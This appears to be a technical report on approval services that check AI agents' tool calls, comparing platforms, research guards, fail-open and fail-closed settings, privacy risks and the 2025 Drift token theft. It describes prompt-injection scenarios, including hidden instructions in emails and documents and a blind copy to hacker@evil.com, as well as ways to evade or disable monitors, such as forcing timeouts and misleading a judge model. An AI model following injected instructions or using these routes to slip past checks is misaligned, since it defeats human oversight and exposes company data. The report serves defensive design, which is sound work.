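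The logic rules and the language model rejected seven of the eight malicious tools and two harmless ones. Adding an analysis of the source code caught all eight malicious tools but raised the number of harmless tools rejected to five, because powerful administrative tools have many of the same abilities as malicious software.

#### Writing a policy for each task

A fixed set of sequence rules suits an agent with one job. A general assistant is harder, because sending money is right when the user wants a refund paid and wrong when the user wants an inbox summarised. Sapien therefore writes a new policy for every task. Suppose the user asks the agent to refund the person who sent them money last week:

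1. Before the agent starts, a language model receives the user's request and the tools' documentation. It receives nothing that an outsider could have written.
2. The model writes a policy, which says that the agent must first list the transactions and may then send money only to a sender, and for an amount, in last week's list.
3. The agent starts work, and Sapien keeps track of its position in the permitted sequence.
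4. If a hidden instruction leads the agent to propose a payment to someone else, Sapien refuses the call and tells the agent which condition it failed.

Some requests, such as "do the tasks on my TODO list", depend on material the agent has not yet read. Sapien first permits only the step that fetches the list, then writes the rest of the policy from the list's contents, so anyone who can edit the list can influence the policy.

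Tiffany and colleagues ran agents with four models on two test suites, AgentDojo and Toolathlon. AgentDojo has 97 short tasks in areas such as banking and travel. Toolathlon has 108 longer tasks in software such as GitHub and Google Workspace. On AgentDojo, agents under Sapien completed one to five fewer tasks than agents without a policy. On Toolathlon, which the researchers ran in full with only one model, the success rate stayed within 4%.

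Sapien's security was assessed by analysis. The analysis assumed that an attacker already controlled the agent completely and checked whether the policy left any way to reach the attacker's goal. On AgentDojo, Sapien's policies ruled out 93% to 95% of 949 attacks, compared with 83% to 87% for a simple list of permitted tools. On Toolathlon, the figures were 65% and 32% of 212 attacks. The gap is wider there because the attacks use tools that the task itself requires, which a list of permitted tools can't exclude.

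Most of the remaining attacks change content. In one Toolathlon task, the agent compiles interview feedback into a file, and the attacker wants a rejected candidate listed as a "strong hire". The agent uses the right tool to write the right file, so a rule about the sequence of actions would not block it.

Sapien also refused 54 calls across 388 attack-free runs on AgentDojo, and the agent followed only 17 of these refusals with a permitted call. In one case, the policy required the name "London Luxury Hotel" but the database had "London Luxury". On Toolathlon, agents resolved 84% of refusals within one retry, helped by Sapien's explanations. In Copilot Studio, a block probably stops the agent, so it might not be able to retry.

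Sapien checks a fixed condition in less than a millisecond, but writing the policy took 43 to 100 seconds on AgentDojo, depending on the model, and an average of 148 seconds on Toolathlon. An approval service for Copilot Studio first receives the user's request when the agent proposes a tool call, and must then respond within one second. The company would therefore have to write the policy in advance, which is realistic for an invoice agent but not for a general assistant.

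### How far the test results can be compared

Four of the five 2026 papers report measurements, but only Sapien reports them for agents carrying out complete tasks. AEGIS includes a demonstration with a live agent, but its figures come from individual calls.

| System | What the researchers tested | Attacks or unsafe cases stopped | Legitimate calls refused | Delay per check |
|---|---|---|---|---|
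| AEGIS | Individual tool calls | 48 of 48 | 6 of 500 | Median 8.3 ms on a local installation; under 23.1 ms for 99% |
| ToolGuardian | 20 prepared scenarios | All unsafe scenarios, with full rules | None, with full rules | No figure; authors call the logic solver's share negligible |
| AgenticRei | Worked examples of policies | No test | No test | Under 10 ms on a single computer |
| Sapien | Complete agent tasks; attacks by analysis | 93–95% on AgentDojo, 65% on Toolathlon | 54 refusals in 388 attack-free AgentDojo runs | Under 1 ms for fixed conditions, seconds with a language model |

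AEGIS and Sapien faced different tests, so their detection figures can't be used to rank them. AEGIS had to recognise known attack patterns, while Sapien had to contain an agent that the attacker already controlled. The second test is much harder, so 65% on it may be a better result than 100% on the first.

The delays also exclude most of the network travel time of a real request. AEGIS and AgenticRei ran close to the software they were checking, whereas Copilot Studio usually contacts a service over the internet. Both would still have most of the second to spare, but a company would need to time its own connection.

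### The context that Microsoft's scenarios require

The three attacks in Microsoft's Defender post show how much a verdict can depend on context. The post gives no detection rates, but it specifies which action Defender blocks in each case.

| Scenario | What Defender blocks | What the call alone reveals | Context that exposes the attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Invoice email with hidden instructions | A search of the agent's uploaded documents | The search terms | The email that started the agent, and the agent's intended job |
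| Shared document with hidden instructions | An email to the attacker's domain | The recipient and the message | The document the agent read, and the source of the data it is sending |
| Probing of a public chatbot | Tool calls that result from the probing | What may be an ordinary lookup | The earlier questions in the conversation |

The invoice agent routinely emails outsiders because its job includes sending a confirmation to whoever submitted the invoice, so a rule about recipients wouldn't help much. Defender receives the triggering email along with the search, so a detector could find the hidden instructions in the email. A judge could flag the search as unrelated to the invoice, provided the service keeps its own record of the agent's job.

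The shared document case is the easiest of the three to handle with a fixed rule, because a list of approved domains would stop the email without any context. A rule based on the order of actions could also stop it, since the agent has just read a sensitive file. Defender blocks the email but not the read, so the sensitive text is already in the agent's context when the block happens.

The service needs the longest history when it checks the chatbot, because a visitor who asks what the agent can do may simply be curious, and a pattern of probing emerges only over several questions. Rules about the user don't help either, since the site doesn't require visitors to sign in. An attacker could also ask the probing questions in one chat and use the answers in a new one, where the service would find no suspicious history.

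#### Different products, different evidence

Two products connected to Copilot Studio can base their verdicts on different evidence. Microsoft says Defender evaluates the wider context of a call, whereas CrowdStrike's AIDR analyses only the tool name and input values.

AIDR would have a good chance of stopping the email in the shared-document scenario, because the attacker's address is one of the input values. It would have much less evidence in the invoice agent scenario, because it would receive the search terms but not analyse the email that prompted them. In the chatbot scenario, it wouldn't analyse the probing questions.

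AIDR can't stop the user's prompt from reaching the agent's model, but the prompt would still help it judge whether the resulting call should run. Pangea says AIDR logs the latest message and the conversation history, so an investigator could later find an attack in text that AIDR recorded but never analysed. Before buying a product, a company should ask which of the fields the product receives affect its verdict.

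### Asking a person

Copilot Studio waits at most one second for a verdict, which is too short for a person to read a proposed action, understand it and answer. Platforms that support human approval use a third verdict that pauses the call until someone decides.

Some services can refer a call to a reviewer for approval. Databricks calls this verdict ASK, AI SDK calls it "requires-approval" and AEGIS calls it "pending". In AEGIS, the verdict suspends the whole agent, so no other tool runs and the model does no further work. A reviewer receives the tool's name, its full inputs and the reasons for concern, and chooses whether to allow the call. The agent's software checks for an answer every two seconds and stops waiting after five minutes.

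A Copilot Studio service could imitate this by blocking the call, asking a manager to approve it, and, if the manager does, allowing the same call when the agent proposes it again. The approval should apply only to the exact input values and expire soon. Otherwise, permission to pay one supplier could cover a different payment.

#### What Anthropic's approval figures imply

Claude Code normally asks users for permission before it runs commands or changes files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* says this leads to approval fatigue, in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve. Flowhat's *Why Anthropic added auto mode to Claude Code* (2026) relays Anthropic's figure that users approve 93% of permission prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* later gave the figure as 97%.

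A high approval rate alone doesn't show that people are careless. Anthropic says most of the prompts are probably for safe, routine commands, and if 97% of requests are harmless, a perfect reviewer would approve 97% of all requests. The number of dangerous requests people stop is a better measure of how careful they are.

In a more direct comparison reported on the website Hyrax, human testers blocked 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands (13.6%), while the auto mode classifier blocked 937 (89%). The testers' rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic has an interest in the result because it makes the classifier, and a fair comparison also needs the number of harmless commands each side blocked. Even so, the 5% rate is too low to rely on tired reviewers to catch attacks.

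Users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code proposes, according to the same article. They may disagree with more of the plans, but the figure suggests that people exercise judgement when asked about a whole piece of work. A company would do better to ask about a few consequential actions, such as a payment to a new account, than about every call.

The verdict also depends on what the reviewer sees. Kaptein and colleagues warn that a reviewer with a lot of context to read and little time may approve without really checking, and that an attacker can reach the approval step through a series of harmless-looking actions. In the example of the email to John Doe, a prompt that reads "Send email to customer?" encourages the reviewer to approve. A better prompt would put the blind copy to hacker@evil.com at the top, with a note that the address isn't in the customer database.

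## When the service is slow, fails or is unavailable

By default, Copilot Studio lets a tool call run if the approval service doesn't answer within 1,000 milliseconds. Engineers call this failing open. A system that fails closed instead stops any call that has no valid verdict. Failing open means an email to evil.com will be sent if the service is too slow to block it. If the service is down, a system that fails closed will hold back even a legitimate email to John Doe.

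### Copilot Studio's error setting

The form for connecting a service includes a field called "Set error behavior", which covers both late answers and errors, according to Microsoft's setup page. The default is "Allow the agent to respond", and the alternative is "Block the query". Pangea describes these as fail-open and fail-closed, and says that with "Block the query" the agent stops and notifies the user.

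In February 2026, however, a note just below these instructions on the same setup page said that an agent goes ahead with the tool if it receives no decision within one second. The note included no exception for "Block the query". Microsoft's developer page also treats a late answer as an "allow" and doesn't mention the setting.

Both passages probably describe the default, but "Block the query" may work only for errors and still let the call run when an answer is late. A company that chose this setting to protect payments would then have no protection when the service is slow. Administrators should test the setting with a late answer and, separately, with an error.

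### How many calls go without a verdict

Take a company whose agents make 50,000 tool calls a day, with 1% of checks missing the limit. That gives 500 calls a day without a verdict. If the company fails open, those calls run unchecked. If it fails closed, each one can stop a whole task. For a task of eight calls, the chance of at least one missed verdict is:

```
1 − 0.99⁸ ≈ 7.7%
```

If every task has eight calls, the company runs 6,250 tasks a day, and about 480 of them stop partway. To keep interruptions below 1% of tasks, the service could miss only about one check in 800. The average response time is a poor guide, since a service that averages 200 milliseconds can still miss 1% of checks. A buyer should ask the vendor what share of answers takes longer than a second, including network time.

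Outages may matter less than slow answers. A service that is available 99.9% of the time is down for about 43 minutes in 30 days. At this company, that would leave about 1,500 calls without a verdict, compared with 15,000 from late answers over the same period. A vendor's availability figure may not count late answers, because a server that replies after 1.2 seconds is still running. The figure may also cover only one component. If each verdict needs three components that fail independently, and each is available 99.9% of the time, the downtime rises to about 130 minutes.

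The 7.7% figure depends on misses being independent, but in practice they cluster. If misses were independent, an attack that needs two calls the service would block would get both through only once in 10,000 attempts. During an outage, a system that fails open lets both through every time. Misses can also depend on the input. If long documents take longer to analyse, an attacker could pad a document until the check times out, without having to deceive the service.

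Successful checks take time too. Eight checks of 200 milliseconds, one after another, add 1.6 seconds to a task. A customer waiting for a chatbot may notice the delay, but it doesn't matter when an agent is processing invoices overnight.

### Google's examples

Google Cloud's instructions for delegating checks from Agent Gateway give examples for custom services, Model Armor and Identity-Aware Proxy, Google's access-control service. Every example has a one-second timeout and sets failOpen to false, so the gateway stops the traffic if the service doesn't answer in time. Copilot Studio also allows one second, but by default it lets the action go ahead if there is no answer.

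Each extension, Google's name for the connection to a checking service, has its own values for both settings. A policy can also select traffic by path or headers. So a company could fail closed for requests to its payments server and fail open for requests to a weather service, as long as it stays within the limit of four custom policies.

Google also recommends combining an access check with a content check. If both fail closed, a call can proceed only when both respond. If each check independently fails to respond 1% of the time, these failures block about 2% of calls.

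Failing closed can also happen too late to stop an action. A content service might approve a request to send an email, then go down before it checks the tool's response. The gateway would then withhold the confirmation even though the email has already gone out. An agent that interprets the error as a failed email might send it again.

### AWS leaves part of the decision to the customer's code

AWS's configuration page for interceptors has no timeout setting and no choice between failing open and failing closed. *Quotas for Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* gives a default limit of 15 minutes for a whole gateway invocation, but no separate limit for the interceptor.

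*Policy-Driven Authorization for AI Agents with Kyverno and AWS AgentCore* (Kotamraju, 2026), a vendor's engineering report, provides the best evidence on what happens when the interceptor fails. It describes connecting the gateway to Kyverno, an open-source policy engine. The gateway failed with an InterceptorException when the interceptor's Lambda function was inside a private network. This suggests that AWS fails closed when it can't run the function, but one reported error doesn't establish that it always does.

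The restriction on private networks may not always apply either. Akto's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore*, the setup guide for a security product that runs as an interceptor, assumes that an interceptor function can work if it has a route to the internet.

If the function runs but the outside service doesn't answer, the function's own code determines whether the call runs. Akto's code blocks the call by default. A customer can set AKTO_FAIL_OPEN to true to let calls run, but this also lets a call run when a human reviewer doesn't answer in time. By default, the code waits up to 30 seconds for each answer from Akto and up to 840 seconds for a reviewer.

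These limits work only if the Lambda function runs for long enough. Lambda stops a new function after three seconds unless someone changes its timeout. Akto tells customers to allow 900 seconds if they use human approval. If a customer sets up the function by hand, doesn't use human approval and keeps the default timeout, Lambda would stop the function before Akto's 30-second limit. Akto's code would then never apply its fail-open setting, and the result would depend on how the gateway handles a failed interceptor.

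A badly formed denial might also let a call through. Kotamraju warns that if the interceptor returns both a modified request and a blocking response, the gateway may ignore the block and run the tool. According to AWS's documentation, however, the gateway returns the response immediately, even if the interceptor also returns a request. Returning only the blocking response is safe whichever account is correct.

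A similar question is what happens when AWS's built-in policy engine is unavailable. AWS's *Test a policy in LOG_ONLY mode* describes a default denial, but it applies to requests that no policy permits, not to an unavailable engine. Classmethod's *When an InternalServerException occurs after linking a Policy Engine* reports an error from a gateway that lacked permission to query its engine, which again suggests that the gateway fails closed.

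### The Kubernetes precedent

Kubernetes, the open-source system for running software across many machines, faced this problem years before agent platforms did. Before it creates or changes something, it can send the request to an outside service, called an admission webhook, to be checked. Kyverno began as a policy engine for these checks.

Each webhook has a failurePolicy, either Fail or Ignore, and a timeout of one to 30 seconds. In the test version of the interface, the defaults were Ignore and 30 seconds. The stable version, released in 2019, changed them to Fail and 10 seconds. Administrators can also limit a webhook to certain kinds of request, so they can block requests to production systems when a webhook fails but allow requests to a test area.

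Failing closed can prevent a Kubernetes webhook from being restarted. A webhook often runs inside the system it checks. If every copy of it stops, Kubernetes sends the webhook a request to approve a replacement, receives no response and blocks the replacement. Administrators avoid this by exempting the webhook's own components from the check. A company that uses an agent to restart failed services could have the same problem, so its staff need a way to restore the approval service without that agent.

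| System | Time for an answer | If no answer arrives | Where the choice applies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copilot Studio | 1 second | Call runs by default; "Block the query" is the alternative | Environment or group of environments |
| Google Agent Gateway | 1 second in Google's examples | Gateway stops the traffic in Google's examples | Each extension |
| AWS interceptor with Akto | 30 seconds by default, if Lambda's timeout allows | Akto's code blocks the call by default | Each Lambda function |
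| Kubernetes admission webhook | 10 seconds by default | Kubernetes refuses the request by default | Each webhook |

A company that uses Databricks' service policies or Defender's hooks should find out the same details before relying on them.

### Choosing by harm and reversibility

The choice depends on the cost of an interruption compared with the harm an unchecked call could do. Failing closed is worthwhile when:

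```
p × L > C
```

Failing closed is worthwhile when pL > C, where p is the chance that an unchecked call is a harmful one the service would have blocked, L is the loss it would cause, and C is the cost of interrupting a task. Suppose an interruption costs $5 in staff time and a fraudulent payment costs $50,000. Failing closed is then worthwhile if more than one in 10,000 unchecked payments would be fraudulent. For a lookup that could cost the company at most $50, the threshold is at least one in ten.

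Companies rarely know p, and it rises if attackers learn to cause timeouts. The loss is easier to estimate, and it depends mostly on whether the company can undo the action.

| Action | Can the company undo it? | If no verdict arrives |
|---|---|---|
| Look up opening hours | Nothing to undo | Let it run |
| Draft a reply for an employee to send | Yes, the employee can delete it | Let it run |
| Change a customer record that has a version history | Usually, if someone notices | Let it run and review it the same day |
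| Read confidential records for a public chatbot | No, the next reply could reveal them | Stop it |
| Email an outside address | No | Stop it |
| Pay a new account | Rarely | Stop it |
| Freeze a stolen bank card | Yes, and delay is costly | Let it run |

Failing closed isn't always the cautious choice, as the last row shows. If an agent can't freeze a stolen card because the approval service is down, the thief has more time to use it.

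### When there is one setting for the whole environment

Copilot Studio's setting applies to every agent in the environment, so an agent that looks up opening hours gets the same treatment as one that pays suppliers. The simplest solution is to create a separate environment for agents whose actions are hard to undo and choose "Block the query" there. Agents that only answer routine questions can stay in an environment that fails open. If one of those agents has a single dangerous tool, it's better to remove the tool than to make the whole environment fail closed.

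If the approval service is still running, it can also choose whether to allow or block each tool when its analysis is late. It sets its own deadline, perhaps 700 milliseconds after the request arrives. If the analysis isn't finished by then, the service returns "block" for a payment and "allow" for a lookup. Copilot Studio receives a valid verdict either way, so its error setting doesn't apply.

A company that buys its service from a vendor could get a similar result with a small relay that forwards each request and returns its own verdict if the vendor is late or completely down. But the relay adds delay and can itself fail, and the company has to connect Copilot Studio to the relay's address instead of the vendor's.

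The tools themselves should also limit the most harmful actions. For example, a payments system can refuse payments to unknown accounts, and a mail server can hold messages to new outside domains, even when the approval service is down.

### Staying within the limit

The service should run its quickest checks first, usually fixed rules and small detectors. It can run slower analysis by a large language model after sending its verdict. If the model then finds an attack, the service can alert the security team and block every later call with the same conversation ID. This doesn't stop the call that has already run, so irreversible actions need rules strict enough to work without the slower analysis.

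Distance also adds delay. A round trip between Europe and the United States takes roughly 100 milliseconds. A new encrypted connection typically needs two round trips before the platform can send its request, and the request and answer take a third, so the total is about 300 milliseconds, not counting analysis. Running the service in the same region as the platform removes most of this delay, and keeping connections open helps if the platform reuses them. The service should also download Entra's public keys in advance and keep spare capacity for busy periods.

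### Noticing missed verdicts

An outage is easy to miss when the system fails open, because users see agents working normally, whereas people complain within minutes when it fails closed. Copilot Studio fails open by default, so companies that keep that default have a greater need for alerts.

The service's own logs omit requests that never arrived, and they can make a reply sent after 1.2 seconds look like a success. The company should therefore compare them with Copilot Studio's audit log and count the tool calls whose verdict was missing or late. It can then run those calls through the service again. This is too late to stop them, but with 500 a day it's an easy way to find an attack that got through.

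The alert threshold should be low. AWS's monitoring guide gives example alarms for an error rate above 5% and for delays longer than one second. At a 5% threshold, the company with 500 missed verdicts a day would never get an alert. A better alarm for a system that fails open would go off after a handful of misses within a few minutes, or after a single miss on a payment.

A regular test call can reveal an outage before real calls run unchecked. Palo Alto Networks provides a fixed prompt that always produces a block, meant for checking a new connection. A company could send it to a test agent every few minutes and raise an alert if no block comes back. The agent should always call a harmless tool, since otherwise the service receives no request. The test environment also needs its own connection to the same service, and a successful test there doesn't show that connections in other environments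 work.

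## Security and privacy risks of the arrangement

An approval service creates security and privacy risks even if it answers every request on time. It receives a continuous copy of what a company's agents read and write, and an attacker who controlled it could decide which calls go ahead. Some of the text it reads may come from attackers, and an administrator can turn the service off by clearing one checkbox. Each risk has a remedy, though some remedies make the service's verdicts less accurate.

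### What the provider receives

Copilot Studio sends context to the approval provider with every tool call, even trivial ones. If an employee tells a human resources agent that she is pregnant, asks about leave, and then asks the agent to book a meeting, the approval request for the meeting can include her identity and the recent conversation. It can also include earlier tool outputs, such as her salary if the agent has just looked it up. The provider can therefore hold data from systems it has no access to, often in several copies, because later requests repeat the recent history.

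Microsoft warns that the provider's data-handling policies may differ from its own, and that the provider may process and store the data outside the customer's region. Microsoft makes the customer responsible for checking that the provider and its terms comply with relevant regulations. A company that chose a European region for Copilot Studio can't assume that its approval requests stay in Europe. A regional address such as Zenity's European one helps, but it determines only where the request arrives. The provider's backups, support staff and subcontractors may be elsewhere, so the contract has to cover them too.

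The provider's logs can also expose personal data. In Pangea's sample log entry, CrowdStrike's AIDR has replaced the social security number in the user's last message with an encrypted value, but the original number still appears several times elsewhere in the entry, including in the findings and the earlier messages. The entry also contains the user's name and location. The sample uses invented data and comes from a different type of connection, so a company should inspect a real entry during its trial. AIDR can be set to log only metadata, which gives investigators less information, but the detection rules still run.

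#### Contracts and data protection law

Under the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the company that runs the agents is normally the controller, which decides why and how to use personal data. The provider is normally a processor, which acts on the controller's instructions. Their contract must hold the provider to those instructions, cover its subcontractors, and require it to delete or return the data when the service ends. Transfers outside the European Economic Area need a legal basis, such as the EU's standard contractual clauses. Any term that lets the provider train its detectors on customers' requests needs close review, because the provider would then be using the data for its own purposes and could become a controller itself.

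*Control 1.8*, which is written for US financial firms, suggests asking a provider:

- whether it processes or stores conversations
- where it hosts the endpoint
- whether it has a SOC 2 Type II report, an auditor's assessment of how its security controls worked over a period
- how quickly it reports a breach.

It's also worth asking how long the provider keeps each request.

How quickly the provider must report a breach matters because the company has its own reporting deadlines. The GDPR normally gives a controller 72 hours after becoming aware of a breach to notify the regulator. *Control 1.8* lists a 72-hour rule in New York as well as duties to US securities regulators. A contract that lets the provider report "within a reasonable time" is too vague. A fixed limit, such as 24 hours, would give the company a better chance of working out whose data is involved.

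Financial firms must keep some records for years, while privacy law favours deletion. *Control 1.8* warns that Defender's alerts don't satisfy US record-keeping rules, and a firm shouldn't assume that another provider's logs do. The firm can keep the official record in its own archive and have the provider delete its copy after, say, 30 days. Disconnecting the service stops new data from reaching the provider, but it doesn't delete what the provider already has.

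#### Sending less

Customers can't customise the request, but they can choose which environments to connect, and they can put a relay in front of the provider to remove fields that are optional in Microsoft's format, such as the chat history and earlier tool outputs.

Removing the conversation from the data sent to an approval service usually makes the service worse at judging intent, but the loss depends on the product. AIDR doesn't analyse the conversation, so removing it shouldn't change the verdicts. A company would be sending AIDR the conversation only for the log.

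A relay can also replace personal details instead of deleting them. It could change customer@foobar.com to person1@foobar.com in both the lookup result and the "to" field. The service could still confirm that the two addresses match and apply rules about the domain, without receiving the real address. Names in free text are harder to find, so the relay would miss some. The rest of the conversation may still identify the person, so the company should treat the data as personal.

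### If an attacker takes over the provider

An attacker who controlled the service could read the requests of every customer connected to it. They could also block every call, which would stop all work that needs tools. Setting Copilot Studio to fail open wouldn't help, because a block is a valid verdict. An administrator would have to disconnect the service, and the agents would run unchecked until the company had a replacement.

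False approvals would be harder to notice. The attacker could answer normally except when a call contained an address they controlled, so the service would still block the company's routine test calls. But an approval doesn't start a tool call, so the attacker would also need to make an agent propose one, for instance through prompt injection.

The damage could be worse on platforms where the service can rewrite a call, such as Google's gateway and AWS interceptors, because an attacker could change the bank account in a legitimate payment after the agent proposed it. This can't happen in Copilot Studio, where the service can't alter a call. On any platform, the best protection is a limit that the provider doesn't control, such as a payments system that refuses unknown accounts.

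#### The Drift theft of August 2025

In one well-documented case, attackers used a trusted integration, Salesloft's Drift, to reach many companies at once. Drift is a chatbot that companies put on their websites and connect to other software, such as their Salesforce customer database. Drift held OAuth tokens for these connections. These credentials let one application use another on a customer's behalf without the customer's password.

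According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Salesloft*, Google's security firm Mandiant found that attackers had access to Salesloft's GitHub account between March and June 2025. They then entered Drift's environment on Amazon's cloud and took the tokens. CyberScoop noted that Salesloft had not explained how the attackers got into the GitHub account.

Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025) report in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* that attackers stole Salesforce data from 8 August until at least 18 August. The attackers exported records such as user details and support cases, then searched them for passwords and cloud access keys that could give access to other systems. On 9 August they also used Drift tokens to read email in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. Larsen said more than 700 organisations were potentially affected, according to Enterprise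 Security Tech's *Google Warns of Massive Salesforce Data Heist via Salesloft Drift Integration*. The Hacker News (2025) reported in September that 22 companies had confirmed an impact.

On 20 August Salesloft told customers about a security issue and urged them to reconnect Drift to Salesforce, but it didn't mention stolen tokens (Krebs on Security, 2025). Salesloft also indicated at first that customers who didn't connect Drift to Salesforce were unaffected. On 28 August Google advised all Drift customers to treat every token connected to Drift as potentially compromised. A customer that relied on the first notice could have left its other connections open for eight days. Contracts with approval providers should therefore require them to report what attackers may have taken, as well as what customers need to fix.

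#### How an approval service differs from Drift

Drift's tokens gave access to its customers' systems. With its webhook, Copilot Studio instead presents the provider with a token that is only for the approval service. An attacker who copied that token couldn't use it to query Salesforce or read a mailbox.

They would still get everything that Copilot Studio sends, which could include the kinds of data the Drift attackers searched for. If an agent retrieves a support case containing a customer's password, the password becomes part of an earlier tool output. McDermott's *Salesloft Drift supply chain attack leads to widespread data theft*, a law firm's client alert, adds that some victims believe the attackers wanted contact and support details for later attacks. Approval requests can contain those details too. Removing passwords and keys from anything agents can read is a sensible precaution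 with or without an approval service.

The difference from Drift shrinks if the provider has a second connection into the tenant. Security vendors use such connections to list a company's agents and find unsafe settings. Customers who follow Zenity's *Microsoft Tenant Integration Using Managed Application Consent* give Zenity's application the System Administrator role in every Power Platform environment, along with permission to read audit logs, user and group details, and employees' interactions with AI. Anyone who stole that application's credentials could directly access customers' environments, much as the Drift attackers did. Zenity's customers switch on the webhook inside an existing Power Platform integration, so they may well have both connections.

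Palo Alto Networks' *Onboard Microsoft Copilot Studio to SaaS Agent Security* describes a narrower connection, with read-only access and a Service Reader role in the environment. However, Palo Alto Networks holds the application's client secret, which is in effect a password. A thief could use the secret until it expired or someone revoked it.

A company that only wants verdicts should ask whether it can use the webhook without the second connection. If it needs both, it should grant only the access the product needs. Zenity lets customers revoke permissions that their setup doesn't require.

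If the provider reports a breach, the company should turn off the webhook, delete its credential and revoke any second connection. It should then search the data its agents have sent for passwords and keys, and replace any it finds. Larsen and colleagues gave Drift customers similar advice. The company can do this search only if it knows what was sent, so it should check beforehand whether Copilot Studio's audit log includes the contents of these exchanges.

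### Text the service can't trust

An approval service that considers context has to read text from outside the company, such as a customer's email or a web page that a tool returned. If the service uses a language model to decide, that text can influence the decision just as it can influence the agent. The request may also include the agent's reason for choosing the tool. If an attacker has already misled the agent, that reason may make a harmful call sound like part of the task.

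In *Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem*, Tran, Dhesi and colleagues (2026) argue that a judge separate from the agent reduces this risk but doesn't remove it, because an attacker may manipulate the context that the agent supplies. They propose sending clear-cut cases to fixed rules and using a context-aware judge only where the verdict depends on purpose or intent. They don't test this design, but their reasoning fits Copilot Studio well, since much of what the approval service receives there has passed through the agent.

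The parts of a request deserve different levels of trust:

| Part of the request | Who supplies or influences it | How the service should use it |
|---|---|---|
| IDs of the agent and user | The platform | To look up permissions and the agent's job |
| Input values | The agent's model, possibly misled by an attacker | To check against fixed rules, because the tool will receive these values |
| User's messages | The user, who may be a stranger | As evidence of the task, if the user has signed in |
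| Earlier tool outputs | Anyone who can write to the source | As data to compare and scan, never as instructions |
| Agent's reason | The agent's model | As a possible sign of trouble, never as grounds for approval |

For actions that are hard to undo, the judge should be able to add a block but not lift one set by a fixed rule. If a rule forbids payments to unlisted accounts, no explanation in the request can get such a payment approved. The judge needs no tools and should be able to return only a verdict and a short reason code, so an attacker who misled it could cause only a wrong verdict.

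Removing all untrusted text from the judge's input would protect the judge, but it would also remove the hidden instructions that might have exposed the attack. A service can instead have a small detector read the untrusted text and return only a score. The judge receives that score, the proposed call, the signed-in user's request and the company's policy, but not the untrusted text. The judge would then be less able to check whether an email faithfully reflects a document, so this design suits payments and deletions better than writing tasks.

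An attacker's text can also affect more than the service's verdict. If the service copies part of a malicious email into an alert, an AI tool that helps the security team investigate may then read that text. Alerts should mark quoted material as untrusted, and the investigation tool shouldn't be able to change security settings based on an alert alone.

### Who controls the connection

A Power Platform Administrator can disconnect the service by clearing the box that permits data sharing in the environment's threat detection settings and saving. Users would notice nothing, just as they would during an outage when the system fails open. According to Microsoft, administrators with this role can perform all administrative functions in Power Platform, even in environments that otherwise restrict access to a security group.

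Someone could also disable the check without changing the Power Platform settings, by deleting the credential in Entra or changing the rules in the provider's console, so roles in those systems matter too. AIDR, for example, has a "No Policy, Log Only" option that records requests without applying any detection rules.

| Change | Who can make it | Effect | Where to look for it |
|---|---|---|---|
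| Disconnect the service | Power Platform Administrator | Calls run unchecked | Power Platform admin log |
| Set errors to "Allow the agent to respond" | Power Platform Administrator | Calls run when the service fails | Power Platform admin log |
| Change the address | Power Platform Administrator, with a matching Entra credential | Another service receives the data and decides | Power Platform admin log and Entra audit log |
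| Delete the Entra credential | Application's owner or an Application Administrator | Requests fail once existing tokens expire, and calls run by default | Entra audit log |
| Remove the detection rules | Administrator of the provider's console | Calls run without a real check | Provider's configuration log |

#### Limiting the roles

Microsoft recommends managing powerful Power Platform roles through Privileged Identity Management (PIM), an Entra service that grants administrator roles temporarily. Compass Security's *Common Entra ID Security Assessment Findings* (2026) lists requirements PIM can set for activating a role, including a written justification, multifactor authentication, and another person's approval. PIM can also limit how long the activation lasts and notify others of it. If the approver works in the security team, an attacker with a single stolen account is less likely to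 be able to disconnect the external approval service.

The need for approval shouldn't delay the response to an emergency. If the approval provider is under attack, someone must be able to disconnect it within minutes, even at night. The company can keep approvers on call, or have an emergency account that triggers an alert whenever anyone uses it.

These activation steps apply to people, not applications. Zenity's tenant integration also registers the provider's own application as a Power Platform administrator, and that application can act without a manager's approval. A provider with that access might be able to change the settings that govern its own connection or a competitor's. The company should list every application with administrator rights and remove those it doesn't need.

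#### Watching for changes

Power Platform's admin log is on by default in every tenant, according to Microsoft's overview of activity logs. It covers changes to settings and typically records the user, the time and the IP address. A disconnection should therefore appear there, but it's best to confirm this by disconnecting a test environment. According to Microsoft, reading the log requires the Audit Logs or View-Only Audit Logs role in Purview, its compliance product. The company should give one of these roles to security analysts who can't change the connection, and alert them to every change.

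If approval requests from a busy environment suddenly stop, that is a second signal that someone may have disconnected the approval service. Switching the setting to "Allow the agent to respond" doesn't stop requests while the service is working, so the company should also regularly compare the settings with an approved copy.

### Independent provider or single vendor

The best reason to add another company's service to Copilot Studio's built-in protection is that it may catch attacks the built-in protection misses. If each misses 10% of attacks and their misses are unrelated, only 1% of attacks get past both, but if they miss the same attacks, the second service adds nothing. Two products from one company are more likely to miss the same attacks because they may share training data and techniques, though an outside product could have the same weaknesses.

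Palo Alto Networks promotes its service as an "independent security layer". This is a sales argument, but there are two reasons to take it seriously: a platform owner wants customers to use its agents heavily, so it may be reluctant to block too many of their actions, and an outside provider can cover several platforms. However, only the provider's verdict is independent, because Microsoft still enforces it.

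The first argument for using a single vendor is privacy. With Defender, the conversations don't go to another company, so there is one less contract to negotiate and one less provider that attackers could break into. Defender also combines its verdicts with other evidence. Microsoft (2025) says Defender joins related alerts into a complete account of an attack, which could link a blocked email to a suspicious sign-in an hour earlier. The analyst firm Directions on Microsoft (2025) says the Defender integration logs agents' tool calls in Purview, where a company may already keep its other audit records.

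Defender's advantage over outside providers is limited in practice. *Control 1.8* reports that blocked prompts may not consistently appear in Defender's search tool, and Microsoft has acknowledged the gap. Palo Alto Networks, an outside provider, says its blocks appear in audit logs and Microsoft's security tools. *Control 1.8* still recommends Defender for most US financial firms, but it advises them to keep preview features away from their highest-risk agents or formally accept the risk.

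Defender is probably the better choice for a company that uses only Microsoft's platform and has few people to vet suppliers. The company can add some independent protection by setting limits in its bank's payment system and its mail server, which apply whether or not Defender approves an action. An outside provider makes more sense for a company whose agents run on several platforms or could do serious harm, provided the company can use the webhook without giving the provider administrator access to its tenant.

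As a third option, a company with strict data residency rules and capable engineers can build the service and run it in its own cloud. This avoids sending conversations to a new security vendor and lets the company write rules that suit its work. It also makes the company responsible for keeping up with new attacks and answering approval requests within a second at any hour.

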